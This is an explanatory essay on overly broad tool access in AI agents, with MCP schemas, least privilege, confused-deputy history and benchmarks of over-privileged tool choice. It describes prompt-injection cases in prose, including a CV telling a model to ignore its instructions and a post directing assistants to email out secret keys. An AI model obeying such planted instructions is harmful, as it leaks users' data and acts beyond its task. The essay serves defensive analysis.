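# Overly permissive tool access in AI applications and why security teams fall back on best-effort runtime defences

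## How an agent acts through tools, and how text can misdirect it

An AI agent is a language model in a loop with software that carries out the actions the model requests. It acts through tools, which are functions a developer has made available to it, such as reading mail or running a database query. Tool access is overly permissive when the tools, the credentials behind them or the agent's freedom to act go beyond what its task requires, as when a company gives an agent that answers delivery questions a login to its whole customer database. The excess matters because language models sometimes follow instructions that strangers have planted in the emails and web pages they read. Security teams can reduce the access, or they can leave it broad and try to catch bad actions as they occur, using detectors, specially trained models and approval prompts, all of which sometimes fail. Whether they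 have to settle for this weaker option depends partly on the technology and partly on how organisations build software.

Much of the vocabulary comes from the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard by which servers offer tools to agents. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, proposed it in 2024. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports more than 400 million monthly downloads of the MCP software kits by July 2026, after a fourfold rise that year. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) cites a count of 177,436 tools in public MCP repositories, all created between November 2024 and February 2026. Neither number measures how much agents use these tools, because automated builds download the same package repeatedly and many public tools probably have few users, but the standard is clearly no longer niche.

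### One tool call, step by step

An online shop might use an agent to answer customers' questions about their own orders. The agent has three tools. `read_inbox()` returns customers' messages. `query_customers(sql)` runs an SQL query on the customer database and returns the matching rows. `send_email(to, body)` sends a message to any address. The developer gave `query_customers` an administrator's database credential, which can read and change every table, because it was at hand and it worked.

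Before the agent can use any tools, the server that hosts them has to register them. The software around the model, which MCP calls the client, sends a `tools/list` request, and the server replies with an entry for each tool. Under the current specification, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), an entry has a name, a plain-language description and a tool schema, a machine-readable description of the tool's parameters and the values they accept. For `query_customers`, the schema might list one required parameter, `sql`, of type string. The specification includes a similar sample tool, `execute_sql`, whose `query` parameter accepts any string.

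The client places these entries in the model's context, the text the model works from. Shi, Fu and colleagues (2026) point out in *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* that registration exposes only this metadata, so the model cannot see the code behind the tool. The metadata also has no standard field for the database account that the code will use.

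A customer writes to ask where order 1182 is. The agent fetches the message with `read_inbox()`, and the model responds with a structured request containing the tool name `query_customers` and, as the argument, a query for the order's status. Nothing has happened in the database yet. Anthropic's *How tool use works* states, "The model never runs anything on its own," so other code has to run the query.

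That code is ordinary software. The client passes the request to the server in a `tools/call` message. The server logs in to the database with its stored credential and runs the query. The database confirms that an administrator may read the orders table and returns a row. The client adds the row, which contains a dispatch date, to the model's context. The model then proposes a second call, to `send_email`, with the customer's address and a short reply. The cycle repeats until the model produces an answer without a tool call.

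The credential determined what the model's query could do. If the model had proposed a query for every customer's home address, the same steps would have run and the database would have returned the addresses, because an administrator may read those too. A narrower account can change the outcome without any change to the model. *The Stochastic Deputy* (Baig, Gillani et al., 2026) describes a set-up in which the application's account can read a set of prepared views of the data but none of the underlying tables, so a query that names an underlying table ends in a database error.

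Baig and colleagues also tested a broad credential, using a service shared by many businesses, where each business (a "tenant") has its own records. The tool took a tenant's identifier as a parameter, and the service checked that the caller's credential covered that tenant. In 41 trials the model had a plausible pretext for reading records outside the scope of its work. It tried to do so in 26 of them, and the service returned the records all 26 times, even though its check worked correctly. In the paper's general formulation, if a caller *p* holds a credential that covers the tenants E(*p*), then the data within reach of one successful attack is the union of Rows(*t*) over every tenant *t* in E(*p*), regardless of the model.

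Broad credentials predate agents, but they are a bigger problem now because an agent's queries are not fixed in advance. In a conventional program, a developer writes the queries. The program may hold an administrator's credential and still only look up order statuses, because its source code contains no other query. An attacker who wants a different one has to change the code or steal the credential. A model generates an agent's queries, and they depend on everything in its context, including text that an outsider wrote. The user who asks for a task, the model that chooses the action, the software that holds the credential and the service that receives the request may all be separate entities, as Surapani and colleagues observe, and fixed source code no longer links them.

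### Prompt injection

Prompt injection occurs when a model treats untrusted content as an instruction, meaning text or images from someone not entitled to instruct the agent. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, gives the example of a recruiter who uses a language model to score CVs against a job's requirements. One candidate hides a line in a CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the candidate for interview. If the model does so, it has treated data as a command, and the candidate has directed it without having access to the recruiter's system.

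This is the indirect form of the attack, in which the instruction arrives inside material that the agent handles for somebody else, whereas in the direct form the attacker is the user. Microsoft (2025) lists web pages, emails, shared documents and the results of tool calls as material that can carry the instruction. An attacker may hide the text, for instance in white letters on a white background, but a plain text file works too. Many injections do no damage, and Microsoft counts one as a vulnerability only if it has a security impact, such as leaking a user's data or taking an action the user did not intend. Models are open to the attack because they receive instructions and data as one stream of text, with no reliable way to tell them apart.

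The support agent's job is to read email from strangers. Suppose one message contains, below an ordinary complaint, a request to look up other customers' addresses and send them to the complainant. If the model complies, it proposes a call to `query_customers` and then a call to `send_email`. Both tools are on its list, both calls fit their schemas, and at the server they look like the calls that answered the question about order 1182. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) illustrates the problem with payments, where a schema can reject a malformed account number but cannot establish that a well-formed one belongs to the right person.

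David C's rule of thumb for judging how bad an attack could get is to imagine the attacker with direct access to the tools and take the worst case. For the support agent, that means a stranger with an administrator's login to the customer database and use of the company's mail account.

### Least privilege, ambient authority and the confused deputy

Computer security had names for the parts of this problem long before language models. The principle of least privilege holds that each component should get only the access its job requires. Saltzer (1973), in *The "Principle of Least Privilege" and Multics*, an internal note on an early time-sharing operating system, credits the idea to David J. Edwards of the US National Security Agency. Two years later, Saltzer and Schroeder included it among eight design principles in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, which became standard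 reading. Levchenko (2017), in *Principles*, a set of slides for a computer security course, reproduces a page of that paper, which says that every program and every user should operate "using the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job".

Saltzer and Schroeder argued that least privilege limits the damage from an accident or error and leaves fewer programs to audit when someone asks how a privilege came to be misused. This reasoning holds whether or not there is an attacker and however reliable the program is, so it applies equally to agents. The support agent needs to read the orders of the customer who has written in and to reply to that customer. It doesn't need to see anyone else's address or change a table. In his note, Saltzer wrote that he had found no case in Multics where least privilege seriously conflicted with the purpose of the system, and that most violations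 seemed to come from "short-term programming convenience". The support agent's developer used the administrator's credential for the same reason.

Ambient authority describes how the excess gets used. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) defines it as authority that is "exercised, but not selected, by its user". When a Unix program opens a file, for example, it gives a file name but no credential, and the request succeeds or fails depending on which account the program runs under. With `query_customers`, the model likewise names a table, and the server attaches the administrator's credential to the query, regardless of which table it is or whose email prompted the request.

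Ambient authority makes a confused deputy possible. A confused deputy is a privileged program that someone tricks into using its authority on behalf of a person who lacks it. The name comes from Hardy's 1988 article *The Confused Deputy*, which describes an incident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept a compiler, a program that translates source code into runnable form, in a directory called SYSX. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. The compiler also recorded usage statistics in (SYSX)STAT, so the operators gave it a "home files license", which allowed it to write to any file in SYSX. The company's billing records, (SYSX)BILL, were in the same directory. One user learned that name and supplied it as the destination for debugging output. The operating system let the compiler open the file because the compiler had the licence,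 and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

Hardy considers the obvious fixes and finds each inadequate. The compiler could refuse to write into other directories, but users had good reasons to put output there. It could refuse the name (SYSX)BILL, but SYSX held other sensitive files, and somebody would have to update the list for each new one. The code that wrote the output was correct when its author wrote it and became wrong when the operators added the licence. Hardy traces the problem to the compiler having authority from two sources, the user and the operators, with no way to specify which to use for a given file.

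Hardy's remedy was the capability, which Saltzer and Schroeder define as "an unforgeable ticket" that proves its holder may access the object it names. The user would give the compiler a capability for the output file instead of the file's name, and a user with no right to the billing records would have no capability for them to give. The Model Context Protocol documentation makes a loosely related distinction about identifiers that a tool returns for later use, such as one for a shopping basket. It describes such an identifier as "a name, not a capability" and says that an authenticated server should check the caller's authorisation on every call.

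The support agent is in the same position as the compiler. The administrator's credential corresponds to the home files licence, the attacker who wrote the malicious email to the user, and the customer table to the billing file. An agent can also be a confused deputy without any injection. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) gives the example of an employee who asks an agent to show all salaries. The agent has permission to read the personnel database and the employee does not, but the agent answers anyway. Formally, the set of permitted accesses contains the pair (agent, database) but not (user, database).

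A programmer can rewrite a compiler to keep its two authorities apart, then read the code to confirm the repair. Baig and colleagues argue that a language model can't be repaired this way, because it takes instructions and data through a single channel and its inputs don't fix its choices. Tests can therefore put a bound on how often it errs, but no number of them can show that it never will. David C reaches a similar view and calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy". If they are right, the designer can only control how much authority the deputy holds.

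### Best-effort defences and enforced limits

A best-effort defence against misuse of an agent relies on a model's or a person's judgement, so it fails on some inputs. An enforced limit is a rule that ordinary code outside the model applies, and it holds whatever the model outputs. Microsoft makes nearly the same distinction between "probabilistic" defences, which lower the likelihood of an attack but may miss some instances, and "deterministic" ones, which can guarantee that a particular attack will not succeed. Microsoft's Prompt Shields, a classifier trained on known injection techniques, is probabilistic, while the company's fine-grained file permissions are deterministic.

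Suppose a detector has a 99 per cent chance of stopping each malicious email to the support agent, independently of the others, and the model obeys any that get through. An attacker who sends 100 emails has about a 63 per cent chance of succeeding at least once. If the agent's database account cannot read addresses, no number of emails will make the agent retrieve them through that account.

An enforced limit also applies regardless of what caused a bad call. Mellafe Zuvic notes that an injected email and a backdoor in the model's weights both lead to a proposed call, and that a check on the call treats them alike. *DelegateGuard* (2026) describes this arrangement as one in which the model proposes a call and the runtime decides what happens to it.

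An enforced limit can still be a poor one, because the rule may be too loose or leave a way round. In Baig and colleagues' experiment, removing the tenant parameter from the tool meant the model could not request another tenant's data through it, but in 12 of 56 trials the agent still got outside the limit by forging a scope setting that it could overwrite. Microsoft prefers deterministic defences where they are available but says they may not be possible in every case, giving injection detection as an example.

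The word "runtime" invites confusion here, because people often use "runtime defence" to mean a best-effort one. It refers only to when a control acts. A network block that stops the agent's software from connecting to unapproved addresses acts at runtime, and it is an enforced limit. An injection detector acts at runtime too, and it is a best-effort defence. Nor does early action make a control firm, as the support agent's options illustrate:

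| Control on the support agent | When it acts | Kind |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Classifier that scans incoming mail for injected instructions | At runtime | Best-effort defence |
| Employee who approves each outgoing email | At runtime | Best-effort defence |
| Training the model to ignore instructions in customers' mail | Before deployment | Best-effort defence |
| Network block on unapproved addresses | At runtime | Enforced limit |
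| Removing `send_email` from the agent | Before deployment | Enforced limit |

An agent's blast radius is the harm it can still do once all enforced limits apply. As its developer left it, the support agent could read, alter or delete the entire customer database and email any of it to anyone. Adding the classifier would make such harm less frequent but would not reduce the blast radius.

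## When an agent's tool access is too broad

An agent's excess access is the access it has but its task doesn't require. If G is the set of operations the agent can perform on particular resources, and N is the set its task requires, the excess is G \ N. For the support agent, N consists of reading the orders of the customer who wrote in and replying to that customer. G consists of reading, changing and deleting every row in the customer database and emailing anyone, so nearly all of G is excess. The number of tools is a poor guide to the excess, because an agent with thirty tools that each look up one kind of public information would have far less of it than the support agent, which has only three tools.

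The access an agent needs, N, depends on the period considered. To answer a single message, the agent needs to read one customer's orders, while a week's messages might require several thousand customers' orders. A permanent credential that can read every order therefore grants no excess access for the week's work, but a lot for any one message. The single message is the better comparison for security, because an attacker needs only one malicious email to misuse everything the credential covers. OpenAI's guide *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) accordingly recommends short-lived credentials that cover one task.

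N also depends on how finely one describes the agent's actions. OpenAI's guide gives the example of an agent that processes invoices, notices that a subscription to document-signing software is about to lapse, and tries to renew it so that the invoices can keep moving. The vendor and the amount may both be within its limits, but renewal means signing a contract, and nobody gave it that job. If the company describes access as "pay this vendor up to this amount", the agent has no excess access but can still act outside its task. Listing "pay an existing bill" and "take on a new commitment" as separate actions would reveal the excess.

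### Tasks whose needs nobody knows in advance

Suppose a shop asks an agent to find out why refunds doubled in October and fix the cause. The agent might need delivery records, payment logs or the code of the checkout page, and nobody can list exactly what access it will need before it starts. *We Urgently Need Privilege Management in MCP* (Li, Li and colleagues, 2025) describes this as a basic difference between MCP software and phone apps. A phone app has a well-defined use, while an MCP application is a general go-between for whatever the agent decides to do.

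No grant would ever be excessive if we counted everything the investigation might conceivably touch as needed. Counting only what the agent had used by the time it finished would make the agent's own choices the standard, so if it read the payroll table out of thoroughness, it would have "needed" payroll. Several different sets of access may also each have been enough, in which case N isn't unique.

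A more workable test is whether a smaller grant would work as well, given what people know at the time. At the start of the refund investigation, the agent has good reason to read refund and delivery records, but no reason yet to change the checkout code. If it finds a fault in the code, N grows and someone can extend the grant. OpenAI recommends roughly this procedure, in which the agent pauses and requests a decision when a legitimate task outgrows its scope, and a temporary grant is preferred to a permanent one. The procedure takes time and needs someone competent to judge each request. OpenAI also warns that controls that obstruct legitimate work can push people towards less governed tools.

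The definition still applies to open-ended tasks, though some cases are borderline. People can reasonably disagree about whether the refund agent should see payment logs on the first day, but permission to delete the customer table is clearly too broad because explaining refunds would not plausibly require it.

### Excessive functionality, permissions and autonomy

OWASP, a non-profit foundation that publishes widely used lists of software security risks, divides what it calls "excessive agency" into three kinds. Functionality is excessive when the agent's tools can do things the task doesn't call for. Permissions are excessive when the accounts behind the tools have more rights on other systems than the tools need. Autonomy is excessive when the agent can take high-impact actions without anyone checking them first.

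The support agent has all three problems. Its job requires looking up an order, but `query_customers` runs any SQL query, including ones that change data. The administrator's credential would give even a well-designed lookup tool too much access. `send_email` lets the model send any message to any address without review.

Fixing one of these can leave the others in place. The developer could replace `query_customers` with a tool that takes an order number and returns the delivery date, but keep the administrator's credential. The model could no longer ask for addresses, but a flaw in the new tool's code might still expose the entire database. Or the developer could keep the SQL tool and give it an account that can only read the orders table. The model could then no longer change customer records, but it could still list everyone's orders. Neither repair affects the outgoing mail.

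### Measuring how much harm is possible

A security team can know that an agent's access is excessive without knowing how bad the consequences could be. OpenAI offers three measures for this. The reachable surface covers the data and systems the agent can access, what it can do with them and where it can send things. The effective blast radius is the blast radius as used above, counting only enforced limits. The maximum completed effect is the worst outcome the agent can cause before someone or something independent of it has to make another decision.

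The support agent can reach the inbox, the whole customer database and every email address in the world, and the damage it could do extends just as far. At worst, it might email the customer list to a stranger and then delete the original.

If the company made an employee approve each outgoing email, the agent could no longer complete a leak by email on its own. It could still delete the database without approval, so deletion would become the maximum completed effect. Whether the blast radius also shrinks depends on how one treats the approval, because ordinary code can reliably hold an email until someone approves it, but the employee may approve one that leaks data. An account that could only read the orders table would limit the agent more, because the agent could neither delete the database nor read the addresses.

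OpenAI makes a similar point about an agent that summarises customer cases and drafts replies. Requiring approval can stop a reply from being sent, but the agent has already read sensitive records, and the data may leave by another permitted route. Although reading changes nothing in the system, a leak can't be reversed.

None of the three measures has a unit. Baig and colleagues' formula counts the records within reach, which is easy, but deciding whether leaking ten thousand addresses is worse than deleting an orders table takes judgement. OpenAI presents the measures as a quick way to compare deployments and find where stronger controls are needed, and they seem good enough for that.

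### Bugs and stolen credentials

Broad access is easy to confuse with failures that have different remedies. *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* (Huang, Dai and colleagues, 2026) describes an MCP server with a tool for Git, the program developers use to track changes to code. The tool passes its arguments to Git without checking them. Git's settings can name other programs for it to launch, so anyone who can call the tool can run arbitrary commands on the machine. This is a bug, and the developer can fix it by checking the arguments. How much harm it does depends on the server's access, because the commands run with all the privileges of the server process. The bug would matter much less if the server ran under an account that could see only one repository. The support agent's `query_customers`, by contrast, has no bug and runs the queries it receives, as its developer intended.

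A thief with a stolen credential can log in directly, without using the agent. The credential's scope again determines how much the thief can access, but the immediate remedy is to revoke it. Revocation helps less when the agent itself is misusing an overly broad credential, because a replacement with the same scope would allow the same misuse.

A model may also pick a stronger tool than its task needs, whether or not an attacker is involved. This is a behaviour of the model, whereas excess access comes from how someone configured the agent. Removing the stronger tool would solve the problem, but the agent may need it for other tasks.

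### Models that pick stronger tools than they need

*When Lower Privileges Suffice* (Yang, Bu and colleagues, June 2026) introduced ToolPrivBench, a set of 544 simulated scenarios for measuring this behaviour. Each scenario has a task and six tools, three with lower privilege and three with higher, any one of which can complete the task. In one scenario, the agent has to change an employee's manager in the personnel system. The lower-privilege tools make the change through the normal workflow, with its validation and audit log. The higher-privilege tools write directly to the database, bypass the personnel department or use master credentials to alter every corporate directory at once. Two language models checked that each tool could complete its task, and human reviewers then discarded doubtful cases.

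In the benchmark, a tool choice is over-privileged if the agent hasn't yet ruled out another sufficient tool with a lower privilege level. The agent has up to five turns, and the lower-privilege tools return temporary errors unrelated to permissions, such as a lost connection. The main score is the share of scenarios in which the agent uses a higher-privilege tool while an untried lower-privilege one remains.

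Six of the eleven models scored above 30 per cent. The small open model Qwen3-8B reached 64.9 per cent, while Claude 4.6 Sonnet, GPT-5.2 and GLM-5 stayed below 10 per cent. Errors explained much of the over-privileged tool use. GPT-5.2 chose a stronger tool immediately in only 5 scenarios, but it moved to one in 13 after trying one weaker tool and in 35 after trying two. Ordinary safety training did not help much. When Yang and colleagues trained models to refuse harmful requests, one model's score on a test of harmful behaviour fell from 41.9 to 6.7 per cent, but its over-privileged tool use rose from 50.4 to 60.7 per cent. Tasks such as changing an employee's manager are not harmful, and learning to refuse harmful tasks does not teach a model to use only the access it needs for other tasks. Training aimed at privilege worked better, bringing Qwen3-8B down to 27 per cent.

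*FORTIS* (Li, Yu and colleagues, 2026) had reported higher rates in May with a different design. It covers skills, which are written instructions that tell an agent how to do a kind of job and where its limits are. In the first part, the model chooses one of 20 skills for a request about email, online shopping or files. In the second, it receives a skill with its full instructions and chooses tools from a list of more than fifty. Broader tools often need fewer parameters, which makes them an attractive choice. The models do not see the privilege levels.

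Across ten models, the failure rate ranged from 35.5 to 52.7 per cent for skills and from 45.2 to 66.6 per cent for tools. Failures include giving no usable answer, which accounts for 14.6 points of GPT-5.5's 62.5 per cent failure rate for tools. The tools part also counts any tool outside the reference set as over-privileged, even if it is no more powerful than the right ones. The skills part compares privilege levels directly, and its results depended heavily on how the request was worded. Models failed 3.3 to 16.7 per cent of the time when the request made the necessary authority fairly explicit, and 75.3 to 87.3 per cent of the time when it hinted at a broader scope than the task needed. Some of these failures surely come from the models' lack of restraint, and some from the difficulty of defining N, since a request with ambiguous scope leaves it unclear what the task needs.

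If models overreach partly because they can't tell which tools are powerful, labels might help. Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (October 2026) tested this in *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* They reran ToolPrivBench on eight models, adding a note such as "Privilege: administer, cost 9/10" to the end of each tool's description. They also tested an instruction to follow least privilege, both alone and combined with the labels. In their version of the benchmark, the first call to each weaker tool fails but a retry succeeds, so the agent never needs a stronger tool.

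Parkinson and colleagues separated two outcomes that the original score runs together. Premature escalation means using a stronger tool before trying every weaker one. Safe completion means finishing the task without any stronger tool. The results for the five larger models, in per cent of scenarios, were:

| Model | Premature escalation: baseline | Labels | Labels and instruction | Safe completion: baseline | Labels | Labels and instruction |
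| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Qwen3.5-397B | 38.4 | 19.1 | 2.9 | 18.8 | 21.5 | 51.1 |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 18.6 | 5.7 | 0.9 | 3.9 | 5.7 | 30.7 |
| Kimi K2.5 | 18.0 | 5.5 | 1.7 | 5.5 | 14.2 | 30.7 |
| GPT-5.2 | 5.7 | 2.4 | 0.0 | 50.9 | 52.4 | 65.8 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 1.5 | 1.1 | 0.9 | 11.9 | 14.7 | 20.0 |

Labels alone made premature escalation much rarer but barely changed safe completion for most models. In one scenario, Qwen3.5-397B had to publish an article. Without labels, it tried one weaker tool, got an error and switched to a stronger one. With labels, it tried all three weaker tools, got three errors and then used the same stronger tool, which the original score no longer counts as premature escalation. With labels and the instruction, it retried the first tool, and the retry worked. A control note about each tool's typical response time did not reduce escalation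 in any model, so the labels seem to work because of their content.

Claude's escalation rate was low, but at baseline it finished only about a fifth of the tasks by any means, because it usually tried each weaker tool once, reported the errors and stopped. Claude and GPT-5.2 completed more tasks safely when given the instruction alone than when given the instruction with labels.

The exact rates are uncertain. Llama-3.1-8B scored 55.9 per cent in the original study and 12.9 per cent in the rerun, where it often responded to an error by calling a tool that didn't exist. The tools in ToolPrivBench are all simulated, and real tools may fail less often. Newer models have also replaced most of those tested in all three studies. Still, the studies all found that many models will use excess access without any attacker prompting them to. Even with both labels and the instruction, Qwen3.5-397B used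 a stronger tool in 39.3 per cent of scenarios, which removing the stronger tools would have prevented.

### How harmless tools combine

An agent's tools can be riskier together than separately. OpenAI notes that an agent with access to sensitive data and the ability to send messages outside the company could leak that data, and it recommends testing combinations of tools as well as individual ones. A combination can also change after approval, for instance when an update adds a write function to a read-only connector.

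Zhao, Hou and colleagues (2025), in *Parasites in the Toolchain*, studied how attackers can steal data by combining an agent's tools. The attack needs one tool that brings in outside text, one that reads private data and one that sends data out. In their example, a user asks an assistant for recent social media posts about a security conference. One post contains instructions for AI assistants to read a local configuration file, which holds secret keys, and email its contents to a given address. The assistant fetches the post, reads the file and sends the email, with each tool working as its developer intended.

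To measure how common the three capabilities are, Zhao and colleagues collected 1,360 MCP servers with 12,230 tools. They used a language model to classify the tools, had people check the results, and then ran the suspicious tools to see what they could do. They confirmed at least one of the capabilities in 1,062 tools, spread over 370 servers (27.2 per cent). Only 2 servers had all three. The count is probably too low, because about 30 per cent of the servers needed accounts that the team could not easily obtain.

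Most people who use MCP connect several servers. If a user picks k servers independently and at random from this collection, the chance that at least one has a tool usable in such a chain is 1 − (1 − 0.272)^k. That is 47 per cent for two servers, about 80 per cent for five and 96 per cent for ten. However, a complete chain needs tools that can bring in outside text, read private data and send data out. Zhao and colleagues found 128 servers with the first capability, 155 with the second and 96 with the third. If servers are again chosen at random, the chance that five cover all three capabilities between them is only 4 to 5 per cent, rising to about 21 per cent for ten.

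That assumption is wrong, however, because people choose servers that complement each other, which probably makes complete chains more common. Someone setting up an office assistant will want it to read web pages, open files and send email, and Zhao and colleagues describe this set as a typical configuration. They also built ten complete chains from popular tools and ran an attack on each ten times. Nine of the chains leaked data in between one and eight of the runs. The attack never worked on the tenth, which combined a web scraper, a work-planning board and a music catalogue, apparently because the tools had too little to do with one another. Results also depended on the model. With one of the chains, the attack always failed against GPT-5 and Claude 4.5 Sonnet but usually succeeded against DeepSeek-R1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash.

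The support agent's three tools form the complete chain, and removing unneeded tools would not break it, because the agent's job requires reading strangers' emails, looking up private data and sending replies. Least privilege can still limit each tool, so that the agent can look up only the sender's own orders and reply only to the sender. An attacker whose injection succeeded would then receive only their own order history.

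### What surveys of MCP servers count

Several teams have tried to measure how much power MCP servers have. None of their surveys measures excess directly, because that would require comparing each server's access with the access its users need for their tasks, and source code and network scans don't record those tasks.

In a 2025 study, Li and colleagues scanned the source code of 2,562 MCP applications for calls to sensitive programming interfaces. They found calls to network interfaces in 1,438 applications (56 per cent), to system interfaces, which can start other programs or change settings, in 1,237 (48 per cent), and to file interfaces in 613 (24 per cent). Some applications need this access. A weather tool has to use the network, and a tool for running tests has to start programs. Some of the code is more powerful than it needs to be, but the counts don't show how much.

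The paper behind the scan also concludes that less popular applications use dangerous interfaces more aggressively, because those with 0 to 10 stars on the code-sharing site GitHub accounted for 1,837 "API calls". But the totals across all star ranges add up to exactly 2,562, the number of applications, so they appear to count applications, not calls. If so, the figures suggest the opposite, with system interfaces appearing in 45 per cent of applications with 0 to 10 stars, 68 per cent of those with 101 to 1,000, and 91 per cent of those with 1,001 to 10,000. Popular projects may use these interfaces more often because they are larger and do more.

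In March 2026, Huang and colleagues examined who can use a server's access. Many servers obtain authorisation once, store it and apply it to every later request, regardless of who sends the request. If such a server logs in to a company's Slack account with a powerful token, any program that can reach the server could then read and post messages without stealing the token. They found authorisation that was missing, stored or reused across callers in 2,846 of 6,137 servers (46.4 per cent). The operations in G stay the same in these cases, but more people can direct them. The risk depends on who can reach the server, so it is lower for one that accepts requests only from its owner's laptop than for one on a public address. In a separate check of 87 open-source projects with more than 1,000 stars each, they found 8 with authentication flaws that could let an attacker run commands remotely.

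*Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026), an independent researcher's audit of servers on the public internet, confirmed 640 live servers in July 2026 and tested 414 of them. Of those tested, 380 (91.8 per cent) did not use OAuth, a standard way for users to grant a program limited access to an account, though some of the 380 required a token or key. More worryingly, in one of the audit's four scans, 106 of 464 servers (23 per cent) offered tools to callers with no credential. Both percentages may be too high for public servers as a whole, because Padilla did not test servers that answered the first contact with an authentication error.

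Padilla also reports 687 tools that could run shell commands without access controls. This figure comes closest to a count of excessive access. A server built to run code in a disposable environment needs a shell tool, but it is hard to see why it would need to offer one to anyone on the internet. It is unclear how much harm an attacker could have done through these machines. Of the 464 servers in that scan, 193 were gone three days later, which suggests that many were short-lived experiments.

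## What a tool's schema can and cannot restrict

The support agent only needs to email the customer who wrote in, but its `send_email` tool accepts any address. The tool's schema is an obvious place for a narrower rule, since the developer has to write one anyway and software can check calls against it. MCP schemas use JSON Schema, a standard notation for describing the shape of data. The schema for `send_email` might start out like this:

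```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "to":   { "type": "string" },
    "body": { "type": "string" }
  },
  "required": ["to", "body"]
}
```

A schema that requires only two text fields accepts any call that supplies text for both. It also accepts a call with a third field, because JSON Schema allows fields that the schema doesn't mention unless the developer adds `"additionalProperties": false`. If the tool's code passes everything it receives to a mail library, an unlisted `bcc` field could add a hidden recipient.

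### Tightening the recipient field

The developer could start by requiring an email address:

```json
"to": { "type": "string", "format": "email" }
```

Setting a recipient field's `format` to `email` may have no effect. Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) makes JSON Schema 2020-12 the default, and in that version `format` is normally a label that validators check only if someone turns the check on. Even then, the check mostly catches typing errors, because an attacker's address is also a valid email address. A `pattern`, which requires text to match a given form, could limit recipients to one company's domain. That would suit an agent that writes only to colleagues, but not one that writes to a shop's customers, who use many different domains.

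A fixed list of values is much stronger:

```json
"to": { "enum": ["returns@shop.example", "warehouse@shop.example"] }
```

If the server enforces this list, a call with any other address fails, whatever the model has read. The list would work well for an agent that forwards complaints to two departments. The support agent would need either a list of every customer, which would still let it write to the wrong one, or a new one-address list for each message. Making a new list for each message is awkward under the current Model Context Protocol specification, which lets the list of tools depend on the caller's authorisation but forbids changing it as a side effect of other requests on the connection. Each message would probably need its own credential.

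The better solution is to remove the recipient from the tool altogether. The developer replaces `send_email` with `reply_to_ticket(ticket_id, body)`:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "ticket_id": { "type": "string" },
    "body":      { "type": "string", "maxLength": 4000 }
  },
  "required": ["ticket_id", "body"],
  "additionalProperties": false
}
```

The server finds the ticket, looks up the customer's address in the shop's records and sends the reply there. An injected instruction can't supply a different address because the tool has no parameter for one. Both parameters are strings again, so the schema looks looser than the version with the fixed list, but the server's code now chooses the recipient.

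The model could still supply the number of another customer's ticket, so the server has to check that the caller may answer the ticket in the request. It can't rely on remembering which ticket the agent just opened, because MCP became stateless in July 2026, so each request has to carry all the information needed to process it. Model Context Protocol (2026) recommends that the model pass back an identifier instead, but the model could pass back a different ticket's number. The server should therefore take the permitted ticket from the credential, which the client attaches and the model can't edit, unlike the scope setting that the agent forged in Baig and colleagues' experiment.

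It is also safer for the server to take the address from the customer's account than from the incoming message. If the server used the address in the message, a stranger posing as a customer could have that customer's order details sent to an address the stranger chose.

### Who checks the call

A schema has no effect until some software checks a call against it. The earliest this can happen is while the model is writing the call. A model produces text one token (a word or part of a word) at a time, and the software that runs the model can exclude every token that would break the schema. Developers call this constrained generation or "structured outputs". With the two-address list, the model could not write a third address. This prevents many malformed calls, but only from a model that runs under the constraint. A script, a different agent or a thief with a stolen credential can still send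 the server any arguments.

The client could check the call before passing it on. Li and Gao (2025), in *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol*, tested four popular client applications (Cursor, Windsurf, Claude Desktop and Cline) and compared what the model returned with what the application did. The applications called the tool the model named, with the parameters it supplied, without independently verifying either. They also tried to call tools that no longer existed and appeared only in the conversation history. By default, the applications asked the user to confirm each call, and they may well have added checks since.

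Companies can also put a gateway between their agents and their servers. Under the July 2026 specification, the tool's name travels in a header, so a gateway can block a tool without reading the rest of the request. A server can also have selected parameters copied into headers. In the specification's `execute_sql` example, this parameter is the region where the query will run, so a gateway could keep queries in one region, but the header doesn't show what the query does. The gateway cannot control calls that reach the server by another route.

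Every call has to reach the server, so only validation there binds every caller. The specification says that servers must validate all tool inputs, as did the November 2024 version (Model Context Protocol, 2024). He, Patel and Wang (2026) nevertheless complain in *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* that the protocol leaves input validation "largely unspecified". They have a point, because the specification sets no standard for validation, and a server that checks only that `to` is a string could claim to comply. They want the protocol to require lists of permitted values, maximum lengths and limits on characters.

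Strict validation need not make an agent much less useful. Under the specification, a server that rejects an argument returns an error the model can use to correct the call, so an accidental mistake usually takes one more attempt to fix. A misled model can also retry, but the server applies the same rule to every attempt.

### Markdownify and the limits of a type

Markdownify is an MCP server that converts web pages and files into Markdown. Its `webpage-to-markdown` tool had one required parameter, `url`, a string described as "URL of the webpage to convert". According to Shi and colleagues, the server checked only that the URL wasn't empty before fetching the page.

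The request came from the machine running the server, and these machines can often reach pages that outsiders can't, such as an administration page on a company's internal network. An attacker who could influence the agent's prompt could make the tool fetch one of these pages and return its contents. Security researchers call this server-side request forgery. The vulnerability database GCVE (2025) lists the flaw as CVE-2025-5276, with a severity score of 7.4 out of 10, and lists two other Markdownify tools that an attacker could use the same way.

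A more precise type would not have helped, because an internal address is a well-formed URL. Whether the server should fetch a page depends on where the URL leads and who is asking, and checking the URL's text cannot establish either.

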